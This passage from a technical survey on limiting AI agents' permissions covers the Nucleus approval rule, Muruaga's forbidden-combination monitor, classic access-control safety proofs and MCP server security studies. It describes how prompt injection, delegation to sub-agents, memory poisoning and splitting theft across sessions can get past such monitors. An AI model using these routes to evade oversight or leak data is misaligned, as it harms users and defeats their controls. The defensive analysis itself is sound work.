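| Require approval | (always, low-risk, low-risk, ask) | The developer must review each push |

Any safe configuration below *U* is safe for one of these four reasons, so it lies at or below one of the four repairs. No two of these repairs are comparable, so there is no largest safe configuration below *U*, and the order gives no reason to prefer one repair to another. Somebody has to choose based on what the task needs and how much of a person's attention each repair would take.

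### How Nucleus chooses

Nucleus always chooses approval. Its rule, as the developers state it in the permissions guide for Nucleus, has three conditions:

- reading files is at "low-risk" or higher
- fetching pages or searching the web is at "low-risk" or higher
- pushing code, opening a pull request or running shell commands is at "low-risk" or higher.

If all three hold, every operation in the last group needs a person's approval. The portcullis source code also counts file searches as access to private data, because search results can reveal file contents. According to portcullis' *Security Policy*, the software applies the rule whenever it loads a policy, so an attacker cannot remove the rule by supplying a doctored policy file. Only a feature meant for testing can turn the rule off.

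Administrators can make the other choices themselves by picking a ready-made profile. The "codegen" profile lets an agent write code, run commands and commit locally, but not access the web. The "pr-review" profile allows reading and web access, but not pushing or shell commands. The "fix-issue" profile includes everything a developer would use, so its pushes, pull requests and shell commands need approval.

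Nucleus treats every shell command as if it might send data, because the shell could be used to send it. In the quick-start guide, an agent with file, web and shell access therefore needs approval to run `git status`, which only lists changed files. Under "codegen", the same command runs without approval. People who must approve many harmless commands may stop reading them, and Nucleus does not protect against a person who approves a malicious one.

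The classification also misses some risks. The rule treats a web fetch only as a source of untrusted text, but the requested address can contain a secret, so an agent that can read and fetch could leak a key without pushing. Nucleus limits this separately with a list of permitted network hosts, though its simplest mode for local development does not enforce the list. The developers describe "pr-review" as having no way to send data out, yet they suggest using it to post comments on GitHub, and public comments can send data out. Untrusted text can also come from a stranger's file in the developer's repository, but the rule counts reading that file only as access to private data.

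### The safety operator cannot preserve the order

The rule works as a function ν on configurations. If a configuration is unsafe, ν changes its last entry to "ask". Otherwise ν leaves it alone. The documentation of portcullis lists three properties of ν:

- ν(ν(*x*)) = ν(*x*), so applying it twice has no further effect.
- ν(*x*) ≤ *x*, so it never adds a permission.
- ν(*x* ∧ *y*) = ν(*x*) ∧ ν(*y*), so it preserves meets.

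The project is named after the mathematical nucleus, a function with similar properties, except that a nucleus enlarges elements and the project's function shrinks them. The Encyclopedia of Mathematics entry *Nucleus* notes that every nucleus is monotone, meaning that *x* ≤ *y* implies ν(*x*) ≤ ν(*y*). This follows from preserving meets. If *x* ≤ *y*, then *x* ∧ *y* = *x*, so ν(*x*) = ν(*x*) ∧ ν(*y*) ≤ ν(*y*). The project's *Formal Methods Plan* therefore lists monotonicity among the laws to prove.

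The proof attempt found the opposite. The developers of Nucleus now report a proven counterexample to monotonicity, which their tests had missed, in which the rule fires for *y* but not for *x*. If ν is not monotone, it cannot preserve meets either, although the library's documentation still claims that it does. Two configurations are enough to show both failures:

| | Configuration | After applying ν |
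|---|---|---|
| *x*, without web access | (always, never, low-risk, free) | (always, never, low-risk, free) |
| *y*, with web access | (always, low-risk, low-risk, free) | (always, low-risk, low-risk, ask) |

Under ν, an agent without web access (*x*) can push freely, but the same agent with web access (*y*) needs approval to push. This means ν does not preserve order. We have *x* ≤ *y*, because *y* differs from *x* only in allowing fetches, but ν(*x*) ≰ ν(*y*), because only ν(*x*) allows pushes without approval. ν does not preserve meets either. Since *x* ∧ *y* = *x*, ν(*x* ∧ *y*) allows pushes without approval, while ν(*x*) ∧ ν(*y*) requires approval.

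Every rule of this kind has the same defect, so it is not a programming error. Suppose a function always returns a safe configuration, never adds a permission, and leaves safe configurations unchanged. It then leaves the research session *A* and the publishing session *B* unchanged. Both are below their join, *A* ∨ *B*, so if the function were monotone, its result on the join would be ≥ *A* and ≥ *B*, and therefore ≥ *A* ∨ *B*. Because the function never adds a permission, the result would have to equal *A* ∨ *B*. But *A* ∨ *B* is unsafe and the function always returns a safe configuration, so it cannot be monotone.

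A monotone rule must therefore tighten some configurations that are already safe. The simplest such rule requires approval for every push, whether or not the agent has web access. It takes the meet of each configuration with a fixed one, so it preserves order and meets, but the developer has to approve pushes even in sessions where no attacker could have reached the agent.

### What this means for security

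Even without monotonicity, the function returns a safe configuration for every input and never adds a permission. Problems can arise in software that relies on monotonicity, most likely during delegation.

Suppose the developer's agent has the configuration *y*, so it must ask before pushing, and it hands work to a sub-agent that needs no web access. If the software builds the sub-agent's grant from the original *y*, before ν added the approval, the result is *x*, and the sub-agent may push without asking, which the parent cannot do. The two agents together then have the whole trifecta, because a parent that has read the attacker's page can pass the attacker's instruction to a sub-agent that can read private files and push without approval.

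Starting from ν(*y*) fixes this, because its "ask" survives every later meet, so the sub-agent must ask too. According to Nucleus's architecture notes, the software applies ν to every permission state and only tightens it afterwards, which is the right order.

The order in which software combines limits can matter as well. In the library, the meet operation itself applies ν, and the documentation shows a configuration gaining an approval when a program combines it with itself. Suppose the organisation and the developer both allow *y*, and the task allows only *x*:

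- Combining the organisation's and developer's limits first adds an approval, which remains after the task removes web access.
- Combining the developer's limit with the task's first removes web access, so ν never adds an approval.

Both results are safe, but the same three limits produce two different grants. The difference disappears if the software applies ν to each limit before taking any meets. All the limits are then safe, so their meets are also safe, and applying ν to them changes nothing.

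### Recording what the agent has done

Testing a configuration shows what an agent could do in a session. If the developer switches off web access mid-session, after the agent has read the attacker's page, the remaining permissions form a safe configuration, but the attacker's instruction is still in the model's input.

Nucleus therefore also keeps three flags for each session, which record whether the agent has accessed private data, taken in untrusted content or used an outside channel. Once set, a flag is never cleared, so switching off web access does not clear the flag for untrusted content. If the agent has already read a private file and fetched a page, a push would set the third flag, so it needs approval.

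The flags don't record which file the agent read or what the push contains. Reading one harmless settings file sets the same flag as reading the private key, and the flag stays set for the rest of the session. ADEPT-50 had the same upward drift, which made data unusable there but only requires an approval here.

The developers have checked much of this by machine, and Nucleus' *Verified Claims* sets out what each proof leaves open. They have proved that only an explicit reset with human authority can clear or reduce the record of adversarial content, but not that the software labels content correctly. They also list 146 places in two components where the code reads files, runs commands or contacts the network directly. The permission check still runs there, but the operation does not go through the verified layer that should carry it out, so a bug at one of these places could bypass the policy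 entirely.

### Forbidden combinations in Bounded Agents

Muruaga's *Bounded Agents*, published in August 2026, makes forbidden combinations part of the grant itself. A grant, which Muruaga calls a scope, has four parts, *S* = (*R*, *A*, *D*, *X*):

- *R*, the resources an agent may use
- *A*, the types of action it may take
- *D*, the classes of data it may handle
- *X*, the pairs of action types that may not both occur in one session.

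An administrator assigns every tool to one action type, and the protection depends heavily on these assignments. The developer could forbid the pair "read secret" and "push". If all reading were one type, the same rule would stop the agent from pushing after it had opened any file, so it could never deliver a fix.

The monitor records the action types that agents use in a session. Before each call, it checks that the agent's identity is valid and that the call fits the scope, does not complete a forbidden pair of action types, and stays within the session's budgets. It also checks that the call belongs to the current task and matches the purpose the user declared at the start. High-impact calls need a single-use approval tied to their exact details. The monitor refuses any call it cannot log. On an idle laptop, 99% of these decisions took no more than 0.24 milliseconds.

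Muruaga's composition theorem covers the case where every outcome the organisation wants to prevent requires both action types in some forbidden pair in *X*. In that case, no sequence of permitted calls can produce any of those outcomes. To produce one, the agents would have to carry out both actions in a forbidden pair, but the monitor would refuse the later action because the earlier one would already be in the record.

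The theorem holds only if *X* stays fixed during the session and the monitor checks calls one at a time. If it checked calls concurrently, one sub-agent could read a secret while another pushes, and each check could finish before the other action reached the record.

An attack can involve several steps, no two of which are forbidden together. For example, an agent might read a secret, write it into a shared document and then message a colleague. The monitor therefore also checks for forbidden sequences of any length and refuses a call that would complete one, even if other calls came in between. The lethal trifecta needs two sequences, both ending with the push, because the agent may fetch the attacker's page before or after it reads the secret.

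This works like the Chinese Wall. The agent starts with all its permissions, and its early actions in the session determine which ones it loses. The order of configurations could not determine this. An attacker can abuse the rule by getting the agent to read a secret early, so that the monitor later refuses a push the developer wanted. This disrupts her work but does not expose her key.

If the user's declared purpose includes both actions of a forbidden pair, the monitor drops that pair from *X* before the session starts. A user who asks an agent to read confidential records and email a summary needs this exception. The composition theorem then covers only the remaining pairs, so some other check has to stop an attacker who wants the agent to read records and send email. The monitor makes no such exception for forbidden sequences.

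### Bounding the damage along a chain

A second theorem concerns delegation. Muruaga gives each resource a score between 0 and 1 for how much harm its misuse could do. By default, 40% of the score reflects how many people or systems are affected, 40% how hard the effect is to reverse, and 20% how sensitive the data is. Each agent has a ceiling on its total score, and whatever its parent has already used counts toward that ceiling. An agent's blast radius is the set of resources in its scope whose individual scores fit within what remains under its ceiling.

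Suppose the user sets the first agent's ceiling at 1.0, and the agent changes a calendar entry, which scores 0.14. It has 0.86 left. By default, each delegation multiplies the ceiling by 0.7, so its sub-agent has a ceiling of 0.7 and, after subtracting the inherited 0.14, has 0.56 left. If both scopes list the same resources, the agents can reach the following:

| Resource | Score | First agent (0.86 left) | Sub-agent (0.56 left) |
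|---|---|---|---|
| Calendar entry | 0.14 | Yes | Yes |
| Shared team document | 0.40 | Yes | Yes |
| Customer's personal record | 0.72 | Yes | No |
| Email to an outsider | 0.78 | Yes | No |
| Production database | 0.88 | No | No |

The theorem is that the blast radius never grows along a chain. Scopes never widen, ceilings never rise and spending never falls, so a sub-agent can reach only what its parent could already reach. An attacker who takes over a sub-agent is held to the same limits as that sub-agent. The theorem doesn't require the blast radius to shrink, so without the cut at each step it could stay the same all the way down the chain. The theorem also covers only one chain, so preventing two sub-agents from each spending the same remaining budget takes a shared record like Wei and Xiong's ledger.

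### Assuming that the attack has worked

Like Zhou and colleagues, Muruaga tests the monitor assuming that the attack has already worked. This is reasonable because attacks on models still sometimes succeed. Muruaga cites a public competition run by the security company Gray Swan, in which some of the 272,000 attacks succeeded against each of the 13 leading models, at rates from 0.5% to 8.5%.

The test software inserts the exact call the attacker wanted after the agent's first legitimate tool call on an AgentDojo task. This tests how the monitor responds when the model has been fully taken over. The test covers 609 combinations of a user task and an attack.

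| Attacker's aim | Success without the monitor | Success with it |
|---|---|---|
| Send out data or money | 75% to 100%, depending on the domain | 0% |
| Delete or destroy something | 38.6% | 4.0% |
| Change something, such as a calendar | 90.5% | 12.1% |

Forbidden combinations account for most of the first row. The other two rows depend on the user's declared purpose, which is a weaker check. In 14 of the 18 attacks that succeeded, the attacker wanted the same type of action as the user. If the user has asked for a new calendar event, a monitor that sees only action types cannot distinguish the attacker's event from the user's.

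The other four attacks deleted files and succeeded because *X* lacked the pair "read" and "delete". Muruaga measures a list's completeness by the share of unwanted outcomes that its combinations cover. The list for office software, where these four attacks took place, scored 100%. The measure counts only the unwanted outcomes that the administrator has listed, so an attack that nobody thought of does not lower the score.

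### One missing pair

InjecAgent shows the harm from an incomplete list more clearly. In 544 of its cases the attacker wants to steal data, and in the other 510 the attacker needs only a single harmful action. Agent Security Bench (ASB) adds 400 attack tools in ten settings, and half of the tools are stealthy and half disruptive. Neither test runs a model. The software takes the calls the agent is assumed to have made and checks whether the monitor would allow the attacker's next call, so every attack succeeds without a monitor.

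| Attacks | Successful with the full list | Successful with an incomplete list |
|---|---|---|
| InjecAgent, data theft | 0% | 39.9% |
| InjecAgent, direct harm | 60.4% | 82.0% |
| ASB, stealthy | 30.0% | 60.0% |
| ASB, disruptive | 0% | 100% |

In InjecAgent, leaving a single pair off the list let about 217 of the 544 thefts through. The theorem remains true because it assumes a complete list, but an administrator who forgets a pair gets no warning that the list is incomplete. The lists are at least short enough to review. Across the benchmarks, they contained three to nine pairs and at most eight longer sequences, because their length depends on the number of unwanted outcomes, not the number of tools.

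A complete list still fails if someone assigns a tool to the wrong type. The stealthy ASB attacks that got through used two data-export tools that the benchmark's classifier had marked as writing. If it had marked them as sending data outside, a pair already on the list would have blocked both. Nucleus runs the same risk when it treats a web fetch only as a source of text.

Forbidding combinations of actions cannot prevent the 60.4% in the second row, where a single permitted action does the damage. InjecAgent's example is booking an unwanted dentist appointment. Preventing this requires a narrower grant or a check on the details of the call.

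Muruaga also ran a simplified label tracker on the same cases. It let through 1.7% of InjecAgent's data thefts, so the coarser method was no worse on this benchmark, possibly because the benchmark's thefts are simple, with one tool fetching the data and another sending it.

### The cost in completed tasks

Muruaga measured the drawbacks separately, using Claude Sonnet 4.6 on 949 AgentDojo pairs. The strict version refuses any call that needs approval, while the interactive version simulates a person who approves it.

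| Domain | No monitor | Strict | Interactive |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office software | 96.2% | 81.5% | 86.7% |
| Banking | 68.8% | 50.0% | 58.8% |
| Travel | 59.8% | 55.7% | 60.0% |
| Team chat | 73.0% | 56.5% | 60.0% |

Across all pairs, the share of completed tasks fell by 13.9 percentage points with the strict version and 8.6 with the interactive one. The smaller drop depends on someone being available to answer, and the figure doesn't count the time that person spends.

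Progent, a system whose administrators write rules for individual tools, did about equally well. In a comparison on a live model, neither system let an attack succeed, and Progent's agents completed 1.6 percentage points more of the user's tasks. The AgentDojo results therefore do not show that rules about combinations protect better than carefully written rules about single tools. The argument for rules about combinations depends on tasks like the developer's, where removing any one of the agent's permissions would stop the work.

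### Attacks split across sessions

Muruaga also designed 23 attacks with full knowledge of the monitor, in 43 variants. Of these variants, 24 aimed at a forbidden outcome, and the monitor blocked 23 of them. In the one that succeeded, the agent read the data in one session and sent it in another. The monitor's record starts empty each session, so the forbidden pair never appeared in it.

The attacker needs somewhere to keep the data between actions, such as a file or the agent's long-term memory, and agents increasingly have both. The Rule of Two has the same weakness if an agent starts a new session to escape the limit and then reads notes it wrote in the old one, because the notes carry material from the old session into the new context.

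A planted instruction can also persist between sessions. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) describes MINJA, an attack that uses only ordinary queries to plant entries in an agent's memory and succeeded in planting them 98.2% of the time. An agent that retrieves such an entry weeks later takes in untrusted text without using a web tool, so a monitor that watches only web tools will miss it.

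Muruaga's threat model excludes attackers who work across sessions, and defending against them would require a lasting record of where data has been. One option is to keep the list of used action types forever, but an agent that had once read a secret could never push again. Labels stored with the data are more selective. Some monitors instead record calls in a graph and look for a path from a secret to an outsider. Evidence on how well any of these methods work over time is thin. Chu reviewed 116 papers published up to April 2026 and found no benchmark that tests attacks spanning several sessions.

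## Predicting whether a permission can leak

So far the agents have used their permissions in different orders, but the permissions have hardly changed. In a working system, people and programs change them all the time. The developer invites a colleague to her repository, a build server issues a temporary credential, and an installer creates a new account. Before the developer grants a permission, she wants to know which people or programs could eventually get it through the changes everyone is allowed to make.

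### The safety question

*Protection in Operating Systems* (Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman, 1976) gave this question its standard form. Its model consists of an access matrix and a finite list of commands that change the matrix. Each command tests whether certain rights are present and, if they are, carries out a fixed series of steps. Each step enters or deletes a right, or creates or destroys a subject or object. In the paper's simplest example, any process may create a file and become its owner, and an owner may give anyone the right to read the file.

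The safety question is whether a given right can leak, meaning that some sequence of commands, starting from the present matrix, can add it to a cell that lacks it. Such a leak may be harmless, since owners share files for good reasons. Harrison and colleagues therefore advise deleting trusted subjects from the matrix before checking for leaks. If the developer wants to know whether a contractor can safely read her code, she removes herself and the colleagues she trusts, then checks whether the right could spread further without their help.

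Harrison and colleagues proved that no algorithm can determine, for every system, whether a permission can leak. They used the access matrix to simulate a Turing machine, a simple model of a computer with a tape of cells and a head that reads one cell at a time. The machine's state and the symbol under the head determine what the head writes, which way it moves and which state the machine enters next. No algorithm can determine, for every Turing machine, whether it will ever reach a chosen final state.

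| Turing machine | Access matrix |
|---|---|
| Cell *i* of the tape | A subject, *sᵢ* |
| Cell *i* + 1 is to the right of cell *i* | *sᵢ* has the right "own" over *sᵢ₊₁* |
| Cell *i* holds the symbol *X* | *sᵢ* has the right *X* over itself |
| The head is at cell *i*, in state *q* | *sᵢ* has the right *q* over itself |

Each rule of the Turing machine becomes a command. Suppose that in state *q*, reading *X*, the machine writes *Y*, enters state *p* and moves left. The command checks that some subject *s* owns *s′* and that *s′* has the rights *q* and *X* over itself. It then replaces *X* with *Y*, deletes *q* from *s′* and gives *s* the right *p* over itself. When the head moves beyond the last cell used so far, a command creates a new subject. At most one command applies at any moment, so the matrix simulates the machine step by step. The right that stands for the final state leaks if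 and only if the machine reaches that state. An algorithm for the safety question would therefore decide whether any Turing machine reaches its final state, which no algorithm can do.

Fixing the commands in advance does not make leaks predictable in general. Harrison and colleagues show that for one particular set of commands, no algorithm can correctly determine, for every starting matrix, whether a permission can leak. If no command can create anything, the matrix cannot grow and an algorithm exists. However, the problem is then PSPACE-complete, so it is at least as hard as the travelling salesman problem, and nobody knows a polynomial-time algorithm for any PSPACE-complete problem.

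The question is also decidable if every command consists of a single step. Such a command cannot both create a subject and give it a right, so creating many subjects achieves no more than creating one. Tripunitara and Li, in *The Foundational Work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, found that the original proof mistakenly ignored commands that delete rights. These commands matter when every cell already holds a right and no command creates new cells, because that right can then leak only after it has been deleted from a cell. Their corrected proof preserves the result, but the result has little practical use because even creating a file takes two steps, one to make the file and one to record its owner.

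An engineer can still prove that a particular system is safe, but the proof has to use something specific about that system.

### A right that leaks in five steps

In 1976, according to the textbook chapter *Foundational Results*, Jones, Lipton and Snyder presented a system in which the time needed to answer the safety question grows only linearly with the system's size. Their take-grant model draws the matrix as a graph. An arrow from *x* to *y* carries the rights that *x* has over *y*, which may include two special ones called take and grant. Bishop (1988), in *The Sharing of Rights and Information in a Capability-Based Protection System*, gives four rules, and only subjects may apply them:

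- **Take.** If *x* has "take" over *y*, then *x* may acquire any right that *y* has.
- **Grant.** If *x* has "grant" over *y*, then *x* may give *y* any right that *x* has.
- **Create.** A subject may create a new node and have any rights over it.
- **Remove.** A subject may give up any of its rights.

Suppose the graph has four nodes. The developer's agent and a build server are subjects. A vault of credentials and a production database are objects, which cannot act. The build server has "take" over the agent, because it runs jobs with the agent's permissions, and "take" over the vault. The vault has "write" over the database. The agent has no rights over anything, yet it can obtain the right to write to the database:

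| Step | Action | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The server takes "write to database" from the vault | The server can write to the database |
| 2 | The agent creates a folder, with "take" and "grant" over it | The agent and the server can use the folder to exchange rights |
| 3 | The server takes "grant to folder" from the agent | The server can put rights in the folder |
| 4 | The server grants "write to database" to the folder | The folder holds the right |
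| 5 | The agent takes "write to database" from the folder | The agent can write to the database |

The folder lets rights move from the server to the agent, although the server's "take" right over the agent would, on its own, move them only from the agent to the server. A similar method lets rights move backward along a "grant" arrow. Two subjects joined by either kind of arrow can therefore cooperate so that either obtains any right the other has, whichever way the arrow points.

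The leak depends on the build server's cooperation. If the developer trusts the server and deletes it from the graph, nothing connects the agent to the vault, so the predicted result is no leak. That prediction is only as reliable as her assumption that nobody can trick the server.

Subjects can create nodes without limit, so trying every sequence of rules would never end. Bishop proves that a search of the original graph is enough. Unless *x* already has a right over *y*, it can obtain that right exactly when all of these hold:

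- Some node *s* already has the right over *y*.
- Some subject is *s* itself or can reach *s* along "take" arrows.
- Some subject is *x* itself or can reach *x* along "take" arrows followed by one "grant" arrow.
- A chain of subjects connects those two subjects, and the path between each neighbouring pair follows one of a few fixed patterns of "take" and "grant" arrows.

New nodes can help carry a right along such a path, as the folder did, but they cannot connect parts of the graph that were separate. Removing rights never helps, because the rules test only for rights that are present. A program checking these conditions needs to track only its position in the graph and in the pattern, so it follows each arrow a limited number of times. Checking a graph twice as large therefore takes about twice as long.

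These rules cover only transfers of rights. Bishop uses a second set for copied information. One of them adds a dashed "read" arrow from *x* to *z* when *x* may read a file that *z* may write.

### What a fixed ceiling changes

Suppose every subject has a ceiling that no command can change, and the monitor permits an operation only if both the matrix and the subject's ceiling allow it. For a right above the agent's ceiling, the answer to the safety question is then trivially no, because the agent can never use the right, whatever the commands are and however long they run. For example, if the agent's ceiling excludes writing to the database, step 5 may still enter that right in the matrix, but the entry has no effect.

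Predicting whether a right within the ceiling can leak is as hard as before, because the ceiling may allow every right needed to simulate a Turing machine. An administrator can avoid the question by assuming that each subject will eventually hold every right its ceiling allows. This assumption is safe, but it may overestimate the rights a subject can actually obtain.

A ceiling also blocks changes that people want. If the database fails at night and the on-call engineer wants the agent to repair it, no ordinary command can give the agent write access to it. Some person or program has to be able to raise the ceiling, and the safety question then applies to whatever that person or program can do.

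A ceiling can also be misleading if the agent can create new subjects, because the agent may give them higher ceilings than its own. And since the ceiling limits only the agent's own permissions, the build server might still write to the database on the agent's behalf.

### Android apps that lent their permissions

Android phones had the second of these gaps. In 2011, users approved a fixed list of permissions when they installed an app. The app could not add to it while running, so a search of the access matrix would have found no leak.

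*Permission Re-Delegation* (Felt, Wang and colleagues, 2011) looked instead for apps that would use their permissions on behalf of others. The study covered 872 apps: the 16 that came with Android 2.2, the 756 most popular free ones and the 100 most popular paid ones. Of these, 320 (37%) had sensitive permissions and also accepted messages from any other app through at least one background component. This made them possible deputies but did not show that they would do anything harmful.

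The researchers traced the code of the 16 preinstalled apps from the points where messages arrive to the system calls that need a permission. They then tested each path by building an attack, and found 15 vulnerabilities in five of the apps. For example, the Settings app turned Wi-Fi, Bluetooth and location tracking on or off in response to messages from its own buttons, but it accepted the same messages from any app. Another app could also make the Desk Clock app sound an alarm and vibrate until the user shut it down. The search probably missed other vulnerabilities, because it could not follow some kinds of call and Android's documentation of permissions was incomplete.

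The 1976 model can represent this kind of borrowing. Harrison and colleagues include a command that gives a subject the right to read a file and immediately deletes that right, which marks the moment when data could pass. But somebody has to know that the deputy offers such a service to write a command for it. Felt and colleagues had to search the apps' code to find such services.

IPC Inspection is a proposed defence that limits what an app can do when another app sends it a message. The system reduces the recipient's permissions to the meet of the two apps' permissions, which is the set that both hold. A prototype stopped all the attacks its designers had found. However, an app may therefore need permissions it never uses itself so that its deputies can work. The defence also does not stop a deputy from saving a request and carrying it out later with its full permissions.

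### Boundaries in cloud accounts

Amazon Web Services (AWS) lets administrators limit a user's permissions with a permissions boundary. According to AWS's *Permissions boundaries for IAM entities*, a user may do only what both her own policy and her boundary allow. In one example, Shirley's boundary covers storage, monitoring and virtual machines, while her policy allows her only to create users. The intersection of the two is empty, so she can do nothing.

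In an example about creating new subjects, an administrator named María lets Zhang create accounts for new employees. Without a restriction, Zhang could create a user with full permissions and log in as that user. María's policy therefore lets him create only users that have a particular permissions boundary, and forbids him to edit or remove it. If he forgets to attach the boundary, AWS rejects the request.

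This prevents Zhang from creating a user whose permissions exceed the company's boundary, but that user's permissions can still exceed Zhang's own boundary. For example, Zhang cannot read files in S3, Amazon's storage service, but he can create a user who can. AWS points out that María is in effect trusting him with S3. The policy also lets Zhang create access keys for any existing user except María. If the company had a second administrator whom María forgot to exclude, Zhang could create a key for that account and use its permissions.

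The boundary's list of allowed services is not always a complete limit on a user's access. A resource such as a secret or a storage bucket can have its own policy naming the users who may open it. Within one account, that policy can give a user access that her boundary neither allows nor prohibits. Only an explicit prohibition in the boundary is certain to block this access.

### Comparing cloud policies automatically

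Cloud policies combine permissions, prohibitions, wildcards and conditions, so it is hard to tell by reading them whether one is narrower than another. *Semantic-based Automated Reasoning for AWS Access Policies using SMT* (Backes, Bolignano et al., 2018) describes Zelkova, a tool that AWS built for this comparison. Zelkova translates each policy into a logical formula about the requester, the action and the resource. A solver then looks for a request that the first policy allows and the second refuses. If there is none, the first policy is ≤ the second.

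For example, policy *X* lets students read an exam and lets teaching assistants read both the exam and the answers. Policy *Y* lets everybody read the whole course folder, except that students may not read the answers. Zelkova can confirm that *X* ≤ *Y*. The reverse comparison fails because *Y* also lets any stranger read the answers, which its author presumably did not intend.

This analysis goes further than Gallo's comparison of conditions because it handles prohibitions. The problem is PSPACE-complete, but real policies are evidently much easier to analyze than the worst case. Backes and colleagues report that Zelkova answers 99% of questions in under 160 milliseconds and that AWS services call it many millions of times a day.

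Zelkova compares policies as they stand and does not model changes people could make to them. A check of Zhang's current permissions would correctly find that he cannot read S3, but it would miss the user he can create. *Cloud Resource Protection via Automated Security Property Reasoning*, a paper from Amazon, notes that preventing escalation often requires analysing relationships between resources in different services. It also warns that tools that match patterns in policy text raise false alarms and miss real problems.

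### The seL4 proofs

The strongest results concern seL4, a very small operating-system kernel that controls access with capability tokens. A running system can contain hundreds of thousands of tokens, so *seL4 Enforces Integrity* (Sewell, Winwood and colleagues, 2011) groups programs and resources into components and uses a policy graph to set the maximum rights each component may have over the others.

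"seL4 Enforces Integrity" proves that if the capability tokens fit within the policy graph before a component calls the kernel, they still fit afterwards. By induction, they fit after any number of calls, so a component can neither gain authority beyond what the policy allows nor pass such authority to another component. A second theorem limits what each component can change. The researchers checked both proofs with the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL, and the results apply to the kernel's C code.

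The theorems require a policy under which no component they cover has complete control over another. If one component can send tokens to another, the policy must treat each as fully controlling the other, so in practice the two count as one. This requirement rules out the kind of connection that let the right leak from the build server to the agent.

Some components need more power than that. One of the researchers' examples is a device that connects a terminal to either of two networks with different security classifications. Its router is a copy of Linux, which has millions of lines of code and is too large to verify, but it doesn't need to be verified because the kernel confines it. A small router manager, however, has access to every network. The theorem about the spread of authority does not apply to this program, so engineers have to verify it separately. Sewell and colleagues also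 left it to later work to prove that components cannot read what they should not, and to certify that the system starts in a state that fits the policy.

### Which analyses work for agents

The safety results above apply to an agent as well as to any other program, because none of them depends on predicting what a subject will request. Harrison and colleagues allow commands in any order, Bishop's theorem covers every possible sequence of rules, and the seL4 proofs cover every call a confined component could make. An agent confined by a kernel is therefore in much the same position as the Linux router. Wei and Xiong extend their criticism of role-based control to all earlier models because an agent chooses its requests as it works, but this is a smaller problem for the safety question than it sounds.

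The Android analysis is harder to transfer because it depended on the deputies' code, where the researchers could see whether a message led to a protected system call. Any text a language model reads might affect any tool call it makes, so a cautious analysis has to assume a path from every input to every tool. The developer also has less reason to treat an agent as trusted and delete it from the graph. Both differences produce more warnings, many of them about leaks that would never happen.

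IPC Inspection reduces an app's permissions when the app receives a request but not when it receives a reply, because apps with many permissions often consult apps with few and would otherwise lose permissions. Felt and colleagues thought attacks through replies would be uncommon, but prompt injection often arrives in replies.

*SoK* (2025), a survey of how agents' permissions can fail to match the trust they deserve, includes a new proof that no algorithm can determine, for every agent, whether the agent will stay within a fixed set of permissions whatever input it receives. Like the 1976 proof, it builds a Turing machine into the system, here through the agent's instructions. The survey presents the result as a failure of fixed permissions, but the result rules out only perfect prediction of what agents will attempt. A monitor can still refuse a forbidden call when an agent makes it.

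Several new tools search agent systems for escalation paths before the systems run. *AgentFlow* (2026) reads an agent program's code and builds a graph of its agents, prompts, tools and memory. It reports a risk when text from a prompt can reach an agent that supplies the details of a sensitive operation, even if it passes through other agents first. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* examines how permissions held by several agents in different parts of a company could combine, and identifies configurations that need an approval step or a redesign.

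Other tools examine servers that connect agents to outside services through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard. *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (2026) tests a scanner on nine deliberately vulnerable servers. The scanner missed all seven servers written in JavaScript when it read their code, but identified all seven as high-risk when it ran them in a sandbox. Because every server in the test was vulnerable, the results don't measure how often the scanner would raise a false alarm.

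*Agent Smith in Action* (2026) describes SCAN-MCP, which looks for harmful chains of tools and provides a working demonstration of each confirmed finding. The developers of one server fixed a flaw in its file uploads within about two weeks of a report. SCAN-MCP examines one server at a time and leaves out chains that cross servers, because data can pass between them through files, web requests, prompts or credentials. The developer's agent could leak her key through such a chain if one server read the file and another pushed the code. Nobody knows what share of the dangerous chains SCAN-MCP finds, because there is no complete list to compare its results with.

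A designer can also make leaks easier to predict by restricting the system, as take-grant does. In *Agenra* (2026), a language for writing agents' permissions, the agent may propose tool calls but may not change the policy or issue approvals, so it has no command for enlarging its own grant. Agenra's analysis explores possible runs up to a fixed limit. Its conclusions hold only if its models of tool outputs and human reviewers' actions include every case that matters.

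All these predictions also assume that something enforces the permissions. Wei and Xiong cite a 2026 survey of 7,973 MCP servers reachable over the internet, about 41% of which offered tools without authentication. The same researchers tested 119 servers that used OAuth and found at least one authentication flaw in each.

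## Enforcement: detecting and blocking an escalation as it happens

An analysis may show in advance that a permission cannot leak, but something still has to refuse the forbidden operation when an agent attempts it. Suppose the developer's agent has repaired the failing test and proposes a tool call that pushes its work to `origin`, the usual nickname for a project's main server. A complete monitor would take six steps:

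1. Identify the caller, by checking a credential that ties the request to this agent, this session and the developer.
2. Resolve the resource. `origin` stands for an address in a settings file, so the monitor looks up the server that the push would really reach.
3. Compare the operation, the server and the branch with the grant.
4. Consult the history, which shows whether the agent has spent its budget, whether the push would complete a forbidden combination, and whether anyone has revoked the grant.
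5. Allow the push, refuse it or ask a person.
6. Log the request, the decision and the result.

Resolving the name once may not be enough, because the agent could edit the settings file between the check and the push. Zhou and Zhang describe a system, ZTAC, that resolves the target before deciding whether to allow the operation, then checks at the moment of use that the operation reaches the approved target.

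A tool can also change after the user approves it. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (Acharya and Gupta, 2026) therefore requires the tool's definition to match the one the user approved. It also caps the agent's effective permissions at the meet of the permissions granted to the agent and those the tool declares. Comparing definitions detects a changed description, but not a server that changes its behavior while keeping the same description.

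### Servers that do not identify the caller

*A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) shows how often the first step is missing among 7,973 MCP servers. The researchers collected 28,715 candidate addresses from two search engines for internet-connected machines, sent each address the protocol's opening message, and kept those that answered as MCP servers.

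| How the server identifies callers | Servers | Share |
|---|---|---|
| It does not | 3,233 | 40.55% |
| Fixed token or key | 2,312 | 29.00% |
| OAuth | 2,428 | 30.45% |

Most of the unauthenticated servers that the researchers examined more closely were tests or demonstrations without sensitive data, so the immediate danger is smaller than the first row suggests. But one was a company's customer database meant for internal use. Anyone who connected could query more than 5,000 records, including customers' names, phone numbers and physical addresses.

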